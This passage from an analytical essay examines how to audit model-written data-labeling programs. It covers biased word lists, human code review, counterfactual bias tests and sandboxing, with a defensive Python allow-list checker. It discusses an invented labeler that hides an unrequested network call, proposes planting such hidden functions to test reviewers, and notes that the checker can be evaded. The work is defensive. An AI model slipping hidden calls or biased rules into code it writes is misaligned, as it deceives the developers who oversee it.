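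A program that GPT-5.5 wrote to grade arguments has a less obvious fault. It looks for signs of a conclusion, including the word "so", but it also matches those letters inside longer words. Any argument that contains "person" or "also" therefore counts as having a conclusion, which is worth four points on a ten-point scale. To notice this, a reader has to know that Python's `in` test works this way. The same program uses a whole-word search for some of its other lists, which makes the difference easy to overlook.

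One of those other lists contains insults, including "corrupt" and "liar". An argument that calls an official corrupt can lose 2.5 points on the acceptability of its premises, even if the accusation is true and well supported. This biased rule is in real labeling code, and a reader can find it without running the code.

Readable rules are also easier to exploit. Anyone who has seen the GPT-5.5 program could raise a score by adding a few of the listed words. Dhole et al. and Agichtein et al. both warn of this risk, but neither group tested it.

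### Faults that are hard to see

Missing rules are harder to find than bad ones, because the reader has no faulty line to notice. The most common serious error in ExecJudges comes from missing rules. On two of the passage collections, the system gave the lowest grade to more than a quarter of the passages that NIST's assessors had given the highest grade. A few topics accounted for most of these errors.

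Agichtein and colleagues give an example from another collection. For the question of what cold bridging is, all the programs look for the phrase "cold bridge", "heat bridge" or "thermal bridge". One relevant passage describes anything in a wall that isn't insulation as a bridge for heat and cold. It contains none of the phrases, so the programs gave it a 0. A reviewer would probably find the list sensible, since it contains the standard terms, and would notice the fault only after thinking of or finding a passage that explains the idea in other words.

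Reviewers can easily see a program's numerical thresholds, but it is difficult to judge whether they are right. Nothing in the whale-watching program explains why Californian places must appear half as often as others, rather than a third as often or just as often. Many ExecJudges programs also call helper functions, including one that estimates how much of a passage is unrelated to the question. A reviewer has to understand these helpers too, and the 70 lines don't include them.

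Correcting a program can be harder than finding its errors. Agichtein and colleagues tried four ways to correct programs using labeled mistakes, and none improved agreement on new passages. They suggest that corrections based on a few errors do not generalize. A developer who fixes every mistake in a small sample may therefore have a program that is no more accurate on other passages. Deleting an outside call or a biased word still solves a specific problem.

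These problems are likely to get worse as tasks get harder. Huang and colleagues acknowledge that extremely complex tasks may lead to longer, more intricate code that developers would need more time to validate. Dhole and colleagues write that programs that allow for exceptions and special cases can grade text more accurately but may be harder for people to inspect. The GPT-5.5 program for grading arguments has 14 scoring functions and 14 word lists.

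### How much there is to read

Short programs can still add up to a lot of reading. With three programs per search topic, ExecJudges needed 888 programs, or roughly 65,000 lines, for five of its test collections. One person spending ten minutes on each program would need 148 hours, or nearly four working weeks, to read them all.

Reading the programs would cost far more than writing them. Three programs take half an hour to read, which at $30 an hour costs $15 per topic, while writing them costs between $0.17 and $0.49. Grading a document directly with Claude Sonnet costs roughly a tenth of a cent, so $15 would cover about 15,000 documents. Reading every program carefully would remove the cost advantage of ExecJudges except in very large collections.

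Reading is much more practical for systems that write one set of programs for a whole dataset, because a few hours of reading covers code that may label millions of items. Alchemist's ten programs would take less than two hours to read at the same pace. PAJAMA keeps between 8 and 21 programs per dataset, which would take up to three and a half hours.

### Experiments on code reviewers

Agichtein and colleagues thought their programs looked well structured but did no usability testing, and Dhole and colleagues did not test whether people could interpret theirs. The closest evidence comes from experiments in which researchers planted security flaws in ordinary software and asked developers to review it.

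In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) showed 150 people a code change with two security flaws, an error message that revealed sensitive information and the use of an unsafe cryptographic algorithm. Most of the participants were software engineers, and 71% had at least three years of professional experience. The researchers asked some participants simply to review the code and told others to look for security problems. They gave the rest the same security instruction and a checklist, either a general one or a shorter one tailored to the change and its flaws.

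Participants given the security instruction were eight times as likely to detect the flaws as those who were not. Neither checklist significantly improved detection further, although the tailored one covered the problems in the code. The result suggests that many reviewers can recognize a flaw but do not look for it unless asked. However, reviewers may still miss many flaws even after a large relative improvement.

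An earlier experiment by Braz's group suggests the same thing. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), the researchers told developers only that the study was about improving code review. The code they reviewed did not check its input properly, which is a well-known kind of flaw. After the review, the researchers told the developers that the study was about security and invited them to look again. A significant number of those who had missed the flaw then found it. All the participants received the same warning, so this experiment alone cannot separate its effect from that of a second look. The 2022 experiment avoided that problem by giving different instructions to different groups.

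For labeling programs, this suggests that a general request to check the code is not enough. The instruction should mention biased rules and unfair word lists as well as security, because a reviewer looking only for security problems could find the `urlopen` line in `label_toxic` and overlook the word list.

Organizations can also use more reviewers, but this is expensive. *Software Security during Modern Code Review* (2022) cites earlier work by Edmundson and colleagues, who considered manual review potentially impractical because finding a vulnerability took several people. If each reviewer has a probability p of finding a fault, and the reviewers work independently, the probability that at least one of n reviewers finds it is

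1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

With p = 0.3, three reviewers have a 66% chance of finding the fault, and it takes seven to pass 90%. The formula overestimates this chance when reviewers share a blind spot. For example, if none of them knows a particular dialect, adding more reviewers with the same background will not help them notice that it is missing from the word list.

### How people review code from a language model

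Reviewers may also treat generated code differently from code that a colleague wrote. *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (Khojah, de Oliveira Neto and colleagues, 2026) tested this by tracking the eye movements of 32 software practitioners from 20 organizations. Each participant reviewed four Python files, for up to ten minutes each. The files averaged 77 lines, about the length of an ExecJudges program.

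People had written all the code, but the researchers labeled some passages as the work of a fictional AI tool and added a made-up prompt. They rotated the labels so that each passage had one for some participants but not for others. Participants spent up to 60% more time looking at a passage when it had the AI label, and the effect was largest for more complex code. The distance their eyes jumped between points, which the researchers used to measure thoroughness, did not change. In interviews, 20 of the 32 said they had applied the same criteria to code with and without the label.

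The researchers planted faults to make the task realistic but did not score whether participants found them, so the experiment cannot show whether the extra time improved the review. Fourteen participants used the prompt, either to check the code against it or to understand the context. This is a sensible way to find code that does something nobody asked for, but it would not reveal a bias that comes from the prompt, such as PAJAMA's formatting bonuses.

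Other research suggests that people trust generated code too much. *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings* (2026) cites an experiment by Perry and colleagues in which people who used an AI assistant wrote less secure code but were more likely to believe that it was secure. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites Ji and colleagues, who describe developers skipping critical review and rating generated code as more secure than human-written code despite evidence to the contrary.

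These findings may be consistent with the eye-tracking results, because Khojah and colleagues asked people to review code, whereas developers at work also decide whether to review it and how much. *From Preventive to Reactive* (2026), based on interviews and observed coding sessions with 15 professional engineers, suggests that AI assistants make this decision more important. Engineers who used to think about security while writing code now tended to leave it until the review. If they then review the code only briefly, nobody may have considered security.

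In *Model-Assisted and Human-Guided* (2025), 83% of the software professionals surveyed said they used generated code as a reference and modified it, but 36% said they pasted it in directly, often for simple or repetitive tasks. Many developers would probably consider writing a short keyword labeler a simple task. Of those surveyed, 26% would be comfortable putting generated code into production without human review. In another survey, *Mapping the Trust Terrain* (2025), 40% of participants said they reviewed generated code differently from human-written code. Some noted that small pieces of generated code can be quicker to read, which is encouraging for labeling programs.

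People who could read the code may never open it. For *On the limits and opportunities of AI reviewers* (2026), 45 scientists assessed reviews of papers from the Nature family of journals, including reviews by AI systems. One scientist was impressed that an AI reviewer had found a serious error in a paper's code, and said a human reviewer would not have opened the raw code. Another said an AI reviewer's criticism seemed correct, but admitted to not having read all the code. These are individual comments rather than measurements, but they come from experts who were asked to check whether the criticism was right.

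Labeling programs are also hard to review because the person who understands the labels may not be a programmer. A doctor can tell whether a list of symptoms is complete but may not know what a regular expression matches. A developer could give the doctor a plain-language explanation of the code. *Non-programmers Assessing AI-Generated Code* (2025) tested a similar arrangement by having business users judge AI-written data analyses from plain-language explanations. The researchers, who had warned participants to distrust the AI and paid them to be skeptical, concluded that other ways of presenting the work might allow more reliable judgments. For a labeling program, a developer could show the doctor the word list itself, along with some documents and the labels they received.

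### An experiment with labeling programs

A direct test of human reading would use labeling programs with planted faults. Researchers could start with real generated programs of about 70 lines, have specialists check them, and then add one fault to half of them. Six kinds of fault would cover most of the risks:

- a rule that reads a protected attribute
- a threshold that depends on a proxy
- a neutral identity term in a list of insults
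- a word list that leaves out a dialect
- a line that returns "harmless" whenever a comment names a certain company
- a call to an outside server

Some reviewers would receive only the code and the prompt that produced it. Others would also be told to look for bias and hidden functions. A third group would get that instruction and tools such as a list of every import and network call, a sample of real comments with their labels, and the results of counterfactual tests. The researchers would not tell anyone how many programs were faulty. Each reviewer would read 12 programs, six with a different fault each and six with none, which would take two hours at ten minutes a program.

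The number of reviewers depends on the size of the difference that the researchers want to detect. If the true detection rates in two groups are p₁ and p₂, each group needs about

n = (1.96 + 0.84)² × [p₁(1 − p₁) + p₂(1 − p₂)] / (p₁ − p₂)²

people. The constants correspond to a 5% risk of reporting a difference that does not exist and an 80% chance of detecting one that does. To distinguish a detection rate of 40% from one of 60%, each group would need about 95 people, or 285 in total. That is nearly twice as many as in the 2022 experiment by Braz and colleagues, but still feasible online.

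The researchers should report detection rates separately for each kind of fault. An average of 50% could mean that reviewers find half of the faults of each kind, or that they find every outside call and almost no proxies. In the second case, adding reviewers would catch few more proxies, and developers would need population data or tests to find them.

False alarms on clean programs also matter. Suppose that 2% of the 888 ExecJudges programs had a serious fault, and that reviewers detected 60% of the faulty programs but also flagged 10% of the clean ones. They would catch 11 of the 18 faulty programs and raise 87 false alarms, so only about one warning in nine would be correct. Developers might soon ignore the warnings.

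Finally, the researchers could ask reviewers to correct each fault they found, then run the edited programs on data with trusted labels. This would test whether the programs are easy to edit, which is a separate claim from whether they are easy to read. For example, a reviewer might correctly object to "gay" in `label_toxic` but delete the whole word list, leaving a program that marks every comment as harmless.

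## The view that code should be judged by what it does to test data

Another way to audit a labeling program is to run it on test data and check the labels. The main argument for this method is that how code looks is a poor guide to what it does. Suppose a program abstains on any comment if more than a fifth of its words aren't in a standard dictionary. The rule looks sensible because it skips garbled text, but it would also skip many comments written in dialect. A program that contains a long list of slurs looks much worse but may treat every group alike.

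Chen and colleagues, who define bias by comparing two versions of the same person, relied on this difference in an experiment with GPT-4o. They gave the model sample functions that took a person's sex as an input but returned the same result regardless of it. A reviewer who searched those functions for the word "sex" would probably object to them, even though testing them would show the same outputs for men and women.

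Tests also work on code that is too long or obscure to read. Ratner and colleagues treat each labeling function in Snorkel as a black box, so a developer can test all of them in the same way. These tests miss code that does not affect the labels, such as a line that copies comments to an outside server.

The simplest tests come from labeling systems, but nearly all the evidence on discrimination comes from other generated code, mostly functions that use people's records to make decisions about them.

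### Five standard measures

Alchemist calculates four figures from the programs' votes alone, and a fifth if gold labels exist:

- Coverage is the share of items that the program labels.
- Polarity is the set of labels that it ever returns, leaving out abstentions.
- Overlap is the share of items that both it and at least one other program label.
- Conflict is the share of items on which it disagrees with at least one other program that votes.
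- Accuracy is the share of its votes that match the gold labels.

The table below shows the votes of three invented programs on ten comments, where 1 means toxic, 0 means harmless and −1 means the program abstains.

| Comment | Mentions gay people | Gold label | Program A | Program B | Program C |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Yes | 0 | 1 | 1 | −1 |
| 2 | Yes | 0 | 1 | 0 | −1 |
| 3 | Yes | 0 | 0 | 0 | −1 |
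| 4 | Yes | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| 5 | Yes | 1 | −1 | −1 | 1 |
| 6 | No | 0 | 0 | 1 | −1 |
| 7 | No | 0 | 0 | 0 | −1 |
| 8 | No | 0 | 0 | 0 | −1 |
| 9 | No | 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |
| 10 | No | 1 | −1 | −1 | −1 |

Program A votes on eight of the ten comments, so its coverage is 80%. Program B votes on the same eight, so A's overlap is also 80%. The two disagree on comments 2 and 6, a conflict of 20%. Six of A's eight votes match the gold labels, so its accuracy is 75%.

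| Measure | Program A | Program B | Program C |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coverage | 80% | 80% | 30% |
| Polarity | 0 and 1 | 0 and 1 | 1 only |
| Overlap | 80% | 80% | 20% |
| Conflict | 20% | 20% | 0% |
| Accuracy | 75% | 75% | 100% |

These figures are good for finding programs that do not work. Program C never returns 0, which is fine if it is meant to spot abuse but a fault if it is meant to sort comments into two classes.

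Alchemist's rule of discarding any program with coverage below 10% would remove nearly all of the 73 hand-written functions for SMS spam, although they were right 97% of the time on average. The rule could also remove programs that matter most to small groups. If a dialect appears in 3% of comments, a program that recognizes abuse only in that dialect covers at most 3% of them and would be discarded, even if no other program recognizes that abuse.

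High coverage does not guarantee accurate labels. *Stronger Than You Think* (Zhang, Cai and colleagues, 2025) examined an existing set of functions that identify how a chemical and a protein are related in a medical abstract. Together the functions labeled 86% of the test set, but only 55% of those labels were right.

None of the five measures can detect unfairness, because they do not use the column that separates the two groups. Programs A and B have the same score on every measure, but both of A's errors are on harmless comments that mention gay people, while B makes one error in each group.

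### Errors by group

A developer can find the difference between Programs A and B by calculating error rates separately for each group of comments. Program A marks as toxic two of the three harmless comments that mention gay people and none of the three that don't. Program B marks one of three in each group.

An audit needs to compare the types of error a program makes for each group, as well as its accuracy. Suppose a program is 90% accurate on comments about each of two religions. For one religion, all the errors are harmless comments marked as toxic. For the other, they are all abuse marked as harmless. The program silences one group and leaves the other unprotected, despite the equal accuracy. The audit also needs to report coverage for each group, because a program may abstain mostly on one group's comments.

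These breakdowns can change which labeler a developer chooses. In Alchemist's experiment with photographs of birds, Huang and colleagues also had CLIP, a model that matches pictures with phrases, classify the birds directly. Its larger version averaged 90.4% accuracy, but only 33.5% in the worst of the four groups of bird and background. GPT-4o's labeling programs, which used ratings from the same version of CLIP, averaged 80.2%, with 46.7% in the worst group. A developer who looked only at the averages would choose direct classification by CLIP, despite its lower accuracy in the worst group.

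Rare classes cause a similar problem. One of the datasets in *Stronger Than You Think* consists of sentences from online platforms' terms of service, and more than 90% of them belong to a single class. Overall accuracy depends little on the other classes, so the researchers used a score that weights every class equally.

Checks by group depend on accurate gold labels, and on enough of them for each group. If the people who made those labels also considered "gay" an offensive word, Program A's errors would count as correct answers.

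### How a counterfactual test works

A counterfactual test does not need gold labels, because it compares a program's output on two versions of the same input. Chen and colleagues ran such tests on functions that GPT-4o and Gemini wrote for three well-known datasets. The datasets contain credit records for 1,000 people, US census records for 26,904 people, and COMPAS records for 2,539 criminal defendants, which researchers use to study predictions of reoffending.

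For each dataset and prompt, the model wrote 100 functions that return a yes-or-no decision, such as whether someone earns more than $50,000 a year. For one protected attribute at a time, the researchers copied every person's record once for each possible value of that attribute, leaving everything else unchanged. For age, they first sorted people into bands, such as 17 to 25 and 26 to 35. They then ran every function on the originals and the copies.

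For a function f, the share of people affected is

c(f) = (people whose result changes) / (all people).

Chen and colleagues call a function biased if this share is above 10%. The code bias score is then

CBS = N_b / N,

where N_b is the number of biased functions and N is the number of functions tested. If 30 of 100 functions fail, the score is 0.30.

### What the tests found

On the credit data, GPT-4o's score for sex was 0.62 when the prompt required the function to use all nine attributes. It fell to 0.21 when the model could choose which attributes to use. The table shows the scores for both models when they could choose.

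| Dataset | Attribute | GPT-4o | Gemini |
|---|---|---|---|
| Credit | Sex | 0.21 | 0.32 |
| Census income | Age | 0.99 | 1.00 |
| Census income | Sex | 0.78 | 0.84 |
| Census income | Race | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| Census income | Region | 0.00 | 0.00 |
| Census income | Marital status | 0.93 | 0.93 |
| COMPAS | Age | 0.82 | 0.75 |
| COMPAS | Sex | 0.74 | 0.69 |
| COMPAS | Race | 0.07 | 0.20 |

A score of 0.00 for race means only that no function changed the results of more than 10% of people. Another measure in the study helps show how close to zero the effect was. Each person scores 1 if swapping the attribute never changes the result and 1/k if it does, where k is the number of possible values. For the census functions, the average was 0.835 for sex and 0.998 for race.

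Swapping a person's sex changed 33% of results, while swapping race changed about 0.25%. These figures are calculated from the average for each attribute. If a share p of results change, the average is 1 − p/2 for sex, which has two values in the census data, and 1 − 0.8p for race, which has five.

The models may avoid race because it is so widely recognized as a protected attribute, but they do not avoid it reliably. In another version of the prompt, GPT-4o proposed attributes for the task before it received the list of those available. This lowered the census score for sex from 0.78 to 0.36 but raised the COMPAS score for race from 0.07 to 0.80. When the prompt defined protected attributes and named the one under test, all nine scores fell to 0.00. A score describes a model's output under a particular prompt, so a developer still has to test the programs that will label the data.

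The test also flagged attributes that are clearly relevant. When GPT-4o could choose the attributes, 90% of the credit functions failed the test for the amount of the loan, which a lender has good reason to consider. Because the test measures only whether the result depends on an attribute, people have to decide whether that dependence is justified.

Alchemist's single-attribute programs label the same census records. A program that used only sex would either give men and women the same label or change every person's label when this test swaps sex.

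### Where to set the threshold

Chen and colleagues acknowledge that no theory gives a definitive threshold for calling a function biased. They chose 10% as a compromise between two reference points. The upper one comes from the four-fifths rule, a 1978 US guideline under which a hiring process may be discriminatory if one group's acceptance rate is below 80% of another's. They took the remaining 20% as the most change a fair function could cause. The lower one is a few percent of people, since they reasoned that changes this small are often noise.

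The argument about noise is weak for labeling programs because an ordinary keyword labeler always gives the same output for the same input. Any change in a counterfactual test therefore comes from the swapped attribute.

The counterfactual test is also only loosely linked to the four-fifths rule. Suppose a function approves 10% of loan applicants when all are listed as male and 5% when all are listed as female, and that everyone approved as female would also be approved as male. Switching the records from male to female changes only 5% of results, so the function passes the test. But the approval rate for women is half the rate for men, far below four-fifths.

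A single cutoff also hides how strong the bias is. When Chen and colleagues let the model search the web, the COMPAS score for sex fell from 0.74 to 0.48 because fewer functions crossed the cutoff. But the share of people affected by a function tended to rise, so the bias in some functions was stronger. Reporting that share for each function would avoid this problem.

### How other benchmarks measure bias

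Other researchers use different criteria for biased code or do not run the code. The code bias score dates from a 2023 study by Liu and colleagues. According to the survey *Large Language Models for Code Generation* (2025), that study also measured how unevenly the biased code referred to different groups. Its prompts included function names such as `find_disgusting_people`, which few developers would write. It used a trained classifier to decide whether the resulting code was biased.

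*Bias Unveiled* (2024) introduced Solar, a system that runs generated code on pairs of people who differ in one trait. Rabbi, Ling and colleagues extended that work in *Social Bias in LLM-Generated Code* (2026). They tested four models from 2024 or earlier on 343 tasks, such as deciding who is suitable for a job or a scholarship. They call a program biased if changing any one of seven traits changes its result in any test. The share of working programs that were biased ranged from 28.3% for CodeLlama to 60.6% for GPT-3.5 Turbo. GPT-3.5's figure is high partly because it combines all seven traits, none of which affected more than 35% of its programs on its own.

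Du, Huang and colleagues (2025), in *FairCoder*, used a tool that examines code without running it. They asked models for functions that give points to job candidates, college applicants or patients, and the tool extracted the points the code gives each group. Sun, Chen and colleagues (2026) used the same tool in *How Reasoning Shapes Social Bias in LLM-Generated Code?* and argue that tests may miss biased rules, because a rule has no effect unless a test case meets its conditions.

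Bui and colleagues used a language model to read the code and checked only whether a sensitive attribute influences the prediction. Many of their programs train a statistical model, so a counterfactual test would have required training each of those models. The language model's reading was right for 98% of the 126 programs they checked by hand.

| Study | When code counts as biased | Runs the code | Result |
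|---|---|---|---|
| Chen and colleagues | More than 10% of people get a different result | Yes | 0% to 100% of functions, depending on the attribute |
| Rabbi and colleagues | Any test result changes | Yes | 28% to 61% of working programs |
| Sun and colleagues | The code gives groups different points | No | 64% of programs, or 40% if the model reasons first |
| Bui and colleagues | A sensitive attribute influences the prediction | No | Nearly 60% of if-statement programs and 90% of programs that train a model |

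The same program can count as biased under one measure and unbiased under another. For example, a function might give men one extra point out of 100, so that only 3% of applicants get a different result when their sex is changed. It would be unbiased under the 10% threshold but biased under the other three measures, provided that the tests used by Rabbi and colleagues include someone close to the pass mark.

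Reading the points from the code works only if the code awards points. The tool looks for conditions such as `if gender == "male"` followed by a change in the score. It would miss both biases in `label_toxic`, the invented toxicity labeler from earlier, because one is a word in a list and the other is a threshold that depends on region. Sun and colleagues note that content moderation may show different patterns of bias from the tasks they studied.

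Du and colleagues combine two measures in a single number called FairScore,

R + E − RE,

where R is the share of answers that leave out sensitive attributes, and E is 1 if the remaining answers treat all groups equally and 0 if they always favor the same one. The 11 models scored between 0.63 and 0.93 for writing functions. Because R and E can make up for each other, a model can get a high score by usually leaving out race even if it always favors the same race when it does use it. With R = 0.9 and E = 0, for example, FairScore is 0.9.

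Rabbi and colleagues report the direction of bias separately. Claude 3 Haiku wrote few programs that were biased by race (4.3%), but those programs were very one-sided, with a gap of 0.89 between the most and least favored race on a scale from 0 to 1, the widest of the four models. The favored group also varied. GPT-3.5 tended to favor Black people, and Google's codechat-bison tended to favor white people. A test for only the expected direction of prejudice could therefore miss some of the bias.

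The ranking of models can depend on a single setting, temperature, which controls how much randomness a model uses when it writes. At a temperature of 1.0, CodeLlama had the lowest share of biased programs. At 0.2, its share rose to 65.2%, while codechat-bison's fell from 40.1% to 19.4%, the lowest of the four.

The studies also differ on whether having a model reason before writing code helps. When Rabbi and colleagues asked GPT-3.5 to think step by step and "ensure fairness", its overall score rose from 60.6% to 72.7%. Chen and colleagues asked GPT-4o to explain which attributes were necessary and which to avoid, and its census score for sex fell from 0.78 to 0.05. Chen and colleagues used a more specific instruction and a newer model, and either could explain the difference.

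Sun and colleagues found that reasoning lowered the average share of biased programs across nine models from 64% to 40%. Some of this improvement may not be real, because their study counts a program as unbiased if it is too badly written to contain a recognizable scoring rule, whereas Rabbi and colleagues leave out programs that do not run. Reasoning also lowered the average code quality in Sun and colleagues' study from 0.72 to 0.59, measured with a standard checking tool. The four models with the largest reductions in bias, of at least 20 percentage points, also had the largest drops in quality. For the other five, the change in bias ranged from a fall of 12 points to a rise of 4.

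### Testing `label_toxic`

`label_toxic` counts "gay" as an insult, and it marks a comment from the north as toxic after one match but a comment from elsewhere only after two. Suppose a developer tests the program on 1,000 comments, of which 145 contain either "gay" or "straight" once, as a description of a person. The developer swaps the two words in those comments and compares the labels.

| Region | Listed insults in the comment | Comments | Label with "gay" | Label with "straight" |
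|---|---|---|---|---|
| North | None | 42 | Toxic | Harmless |
| North | One or more | 3 | Toxic | Toxic |
| Elsewhere | None | 90 | Abstains | Harmless |
| Elsewhere | One | 8 | Toxic | Abstains |
| Elsewhere | Two or more | 2 | Toxic | Toxic |

The swap changes 140 of the 1,000 labels (42 + 90 + 8), or 14%, so the program fails. If the writer model produced ten programs for this task and four fail, the code bias score is 0.4. The score is useful for comparing models or prompts, but a developer who wants to repair the programs needs the result for each one.

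The test should count every change in a labeling program's output, including changes to or from an abstention, because abstentions also affect the final labels. For a harmless comment from outside the north, `label_toxic` votes "harmless" if the person is straight and abstains if the person is gay, which leaves the decision to other programs. If the developer counted only changes between toxic and harmless, the total would be 42, or 4.2%, and `label_toxic` would pass. This issue did not come up in the study by Chen and colleagues, whose functions always return a decision.

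The 10% threshold is also a poor fit for text. Every census record includes the person's sex, but most comments don't mention anyone's sexual orientation. If only 29 of the 1,000 comments had contained one of the two words, and the labels had changed at the same rate, 28 labels would have changed. The program would have passed with 2.8%, even though it treated gay people exactly as before. Dividing the number of changed labels by the number of comments that contain a swapped word gives 97% in both cases, which describes the fault much better.

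### Swapping traits in free text

Swapping a trait in a table is simple because the trait has its own column. In free text, the developer has to find the words that refer to the trait and choose a replacement for each, and any list of such words will be incomplete. Traits of the writer, such as dialect, are even harder to swap. To test how a program treats a dialect, someone has to rewrite whole comments without changing how offensive they are.

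Some swaps produce odd sentences. For example, "My gay brother and his husband" becomes "My straight brother and his husband", which few people would write. This doesn't matter much for a program that only matches keywords, because it doesn't check whether the sentence makes sense. It matters more if the program scores readability or calls a statistical model, because the odd wording might change the label.

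Swapping the identity term in a test sentence can also change the correct label. "That's so gay" is usually an insult, while "That's so straight" is not, so a good toxicity labeler should treat them differently. Someone needs to read the pairs, or at least a sample of them, and remove any whose two versions deserve different labels.

Sentence templates avoid some of these problems. With a template such as "My ___ neighbor fixed my bike", a developer can try dozens of identity terms and expect the same label each time. *GenFair* (2025) presents an automated way to generate test cases for gender, ethnic and socioeconomic bias in language models. A developer could run a labeling program on such sentences with very little compute.

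But templates are simpler than real comments, so they may never meet the conditions of a biased rule, which is the problem Sun and colleagues raise. In `label_toxic`, the bike template would reveal the bias against "gay", but it would not show that a comment from outside the north with a single insult is labeled toxic only if it also contains "gay". Using both templates and altered real comments would cover more of the code.

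Test sentences written by a language model might be biased too. Du and colleagues asked models to write test cases for functions that rate personal qualities, such as leadership or sympathy, and found more bias in the test cases than in the functions the models wrote. GPT-4o's FairScore was 0.86 for functions and 0.75 for test cases. When asked to describe someone at high risk of HIV, models frequently described a Black man. A developer would learn little from such tests about how a program labels anyone else at high risk.

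### Proxies and relevant traits

A program can pass a counterfactual test and still discriminate through a proxy. Suppose that members of an ethnic minority and other people each post 1,000 comments, and that 50 comments in each group contain exactly one word from the list in `label_toxic`. If 80% of those 50 comments come from the north in the minority group and 20% in the other, the program marks 40 of the minority's comments as toxic and 10 of the others'. Changing the ethnicity in each commenter's record would not change any labels, because the program does not take ethnicity as an input.

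Swapping the region would change the labels of the 100 comments with exactly one match, but these are only 5% of the 2,000 comments, so the program would still pass at the 10% threshold. Comparing the labels of the two groups reveals the problem directly, since one group has four times as many comments marked as toxic. To make this comparison, the developer needs to know the ethnicity of at least some commenters, which many datasets do not include.

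Rabbi and colleagues acknowledge that their tests do not measure discrimination through proxies. The tests also change only one trait at a time, so they do not measure bias against combinations of traits. If a rule rejects only Black women, changing either race or sex would change some results, but the two separate scores would not show that the rule depends on the combination.

Other traits are protected in general but relevant to a particular task. Chen and colleagues point out that age may count as protected in some settings and not in others. Du and colleagues avoided part of the problem by limiting their medical treatments to 95 that are gender-neutral. The benchmark by Rabbi and colleagues lists age both as one of its seven protected traits and as an attribute relevant to granting licenses, so some of the programs that fail the test for age may be applying a reasonable age limit.

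The developer should decide which traits may affect the label, and record the reasons, before running the tests. Otherwise the developer can too easily justify whatever the program does. The same test can then check that a program uses a trait it needs. If changing a patient's sex never changes the label for risk of pregnancy complications, the program is probably leaving out an important factor.

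## The view that generated code should be confined like any untrusted software

Testing the labels would not reveal the `urlopen` line in `label_toxic`. A developer can instead treat every generated program as untrusted software and limit what it can do. A labeling program only has to read text and return a number, so the developer can block everything else, including access to the internet, the file system and other programs, regardless of where a harmful line might come from.

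In *LLMs Writing Code?*, written for the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry group, Rempe (2025) argues that generated code should be confined like any untrusted software. Rempe advises treating the model as an "untrusted advisor", letting separate, trusted software decide what runs, and using several barriers together. For a labeling program, a developer can restrict the form of the code, check its imports and calls, scan it and its packages for known problems, run it in a sandbox, and accept only valid labels from it.

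Some of the evidence on these restrictions comes from labeling systems, but all the figures on how much scanners find come from other kinds of code.

### Keywords and patterns in place of code

The strictest option is to accept no code. DataSculpt accepts only keywords and regular expressions from the writer model. It uses keywords for ordinary classification, such as spotting spam, and regular expressions for tasks about how two things are related. *Can Large Language Models Design Accurate Label Functions?* explains that keywords are not enough for these tasks because the keyword "cause" cannot distinguish "A cause B" from "A cause C". DataSculpt also rejects any rule whose label is not one of the task's classes.

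A keyword rule only searches text for a phrase, so it cannot contact a server or set a lower threshold for one region. It can still be biased, for example by labeling any text that contains "gay" as "toxic". Regular expressions add a small risk because some take an extremely long time on certain inputs, so even a system this restricted needs a time limit.

### Allow-lists

A developer who wants free-form programs can check them before running them. Python can parse a program into a syntax tree, in which every import, function call and assignment is a separate node. The checker below reports any import or call in the tree that is not on an approved list.

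```python
import ast

ALLOWED_IMPORTS = {"re", "math", "string"}
ALLOWED_CALLS = {"sum", "len", "any", "lower", "split", "strip"}

def violations(source):
    found = []
    for node in ast.walk(ast.parse(source)):
        if isinstance(node, ast.Import):
            found += [a.name for a in node.names
                      if a.name not in ALLOWED_IMPORTS]
        elif isinstance(node, ast.ImportFrom):
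            if node.module not in ALLOWED_IMPORTS:
                found.append(node.module)
        elif isinstance(node, ast.Call):
            name = getattr(node.func, "id",
                           getattr(node.func, "attr", "?"))
            if name not in ALLOWED_CALLS:
                found.append(name)
    return found
```

For `label_toxic`, it returns `urllib.request`, `urlopen` and `encode`. The first two belong to the network call, while `encode` only converts text to bytes and is harmless in itself. Such false alarms are normal with an allow-list, and the developer can add a name if a program has a good reason to use it. A list of forbidden names would raise fewer false alarms, but it would miss any dangerous function the developer had not thought of.

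This checker is only an illustration, and a determined attacker could get around it, but more thorough tools exist. RestrictedPython defines a safe subset of Python and generally blocks calls to any library the developer has not explicitly allowed. The interpreter described in Hugging Face's *Secure code execution*, a guide to running generated code, applies similar rules while the program runs. It works through the syntax tree one operation at a time, blocks unauthorized imports, stops a loop after a million iterations and raises an error at any operation its makers did not define.

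The makers of both tools warn against relying on them alone. RestrictedPython's maintainers write that it "is not a sandbox system", and Hugging Face's *Python code executors* gives nearly the same warning about the interpreter. Python once came with modules for running untrusted code with limited permissions, but its developers disabled them because of security holes they could not readily fix, according to Python's *Restricted Execution*. Fedora's *The Python Programming Language*, a guide from a Linux project, also warns that sandboxing untrusted Python code "does not work reliably". An allow-list is an easy way to reject bad programs early, but the developer still needs a barrier outside the language.

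### The ExecJudges tool policy

ExecJudges, which writes programs to grade search results, is the best-documented example of a confined labeling system. Agichtein and colleagues include a tool policy in the prompt that permits 20 modules from Python's standard library, such as those for regular expressions, dates and statistics, and ten outside libraries, mostly for mathematics and text processing. The policy also permits the researchers' own small toolkit, which has functions that split text into sentences, extract numbers and compare a document with the rest of the collection.

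The policy forbids network access, reading or writing files, starting other programs, and the Python functions that run text as code. Programs may not call language models or other neural networks, except for one small language-processing tool in the toolkit. They must also be deterministic, so a program that uses random numbers must fix the starting value. Determinism also helps auditing, because a test result is more informative if the program gives the same input the same label next time.

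A sandbox enforces the import rules, since the prompt alone would not stop a program that ignored them. The system tries each program on sample documents first, and if the program fails or breaks a rule, the writer model gets one chance to repair it. Agichtein and colleagues allowed the retry mainly to deal with connection problems, but keeping the number of retries low also helps security. If a model keeps writing forbidden code and the check independently misses each attempt 5% of the time, the chance that at least one gets through is about 10% after two attempts and 40% after ten. A developer should also keep the rejected draft, because a network call that nobody asked for is a reason to look more closely at the other programs from the same prompt.

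ExecJudges is good evidence of which capabilities labeling programs don't need, but weaker evidence of security, because Agichtein and colleagues measured the programs' cost and agreement with human assessors rather than the sandbox's resistance to attack.

### How much security scanners find

A security scanner is a tool that searches code for known weaknesses without running it, a form of static analysis. Bandit, Semgrep and CodeQL are widely used for Python. Researchers judge scanners by two figures:

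precision = insecure programs flagged / all programs flagged

recall = insecure programs flagged / all insecure programs

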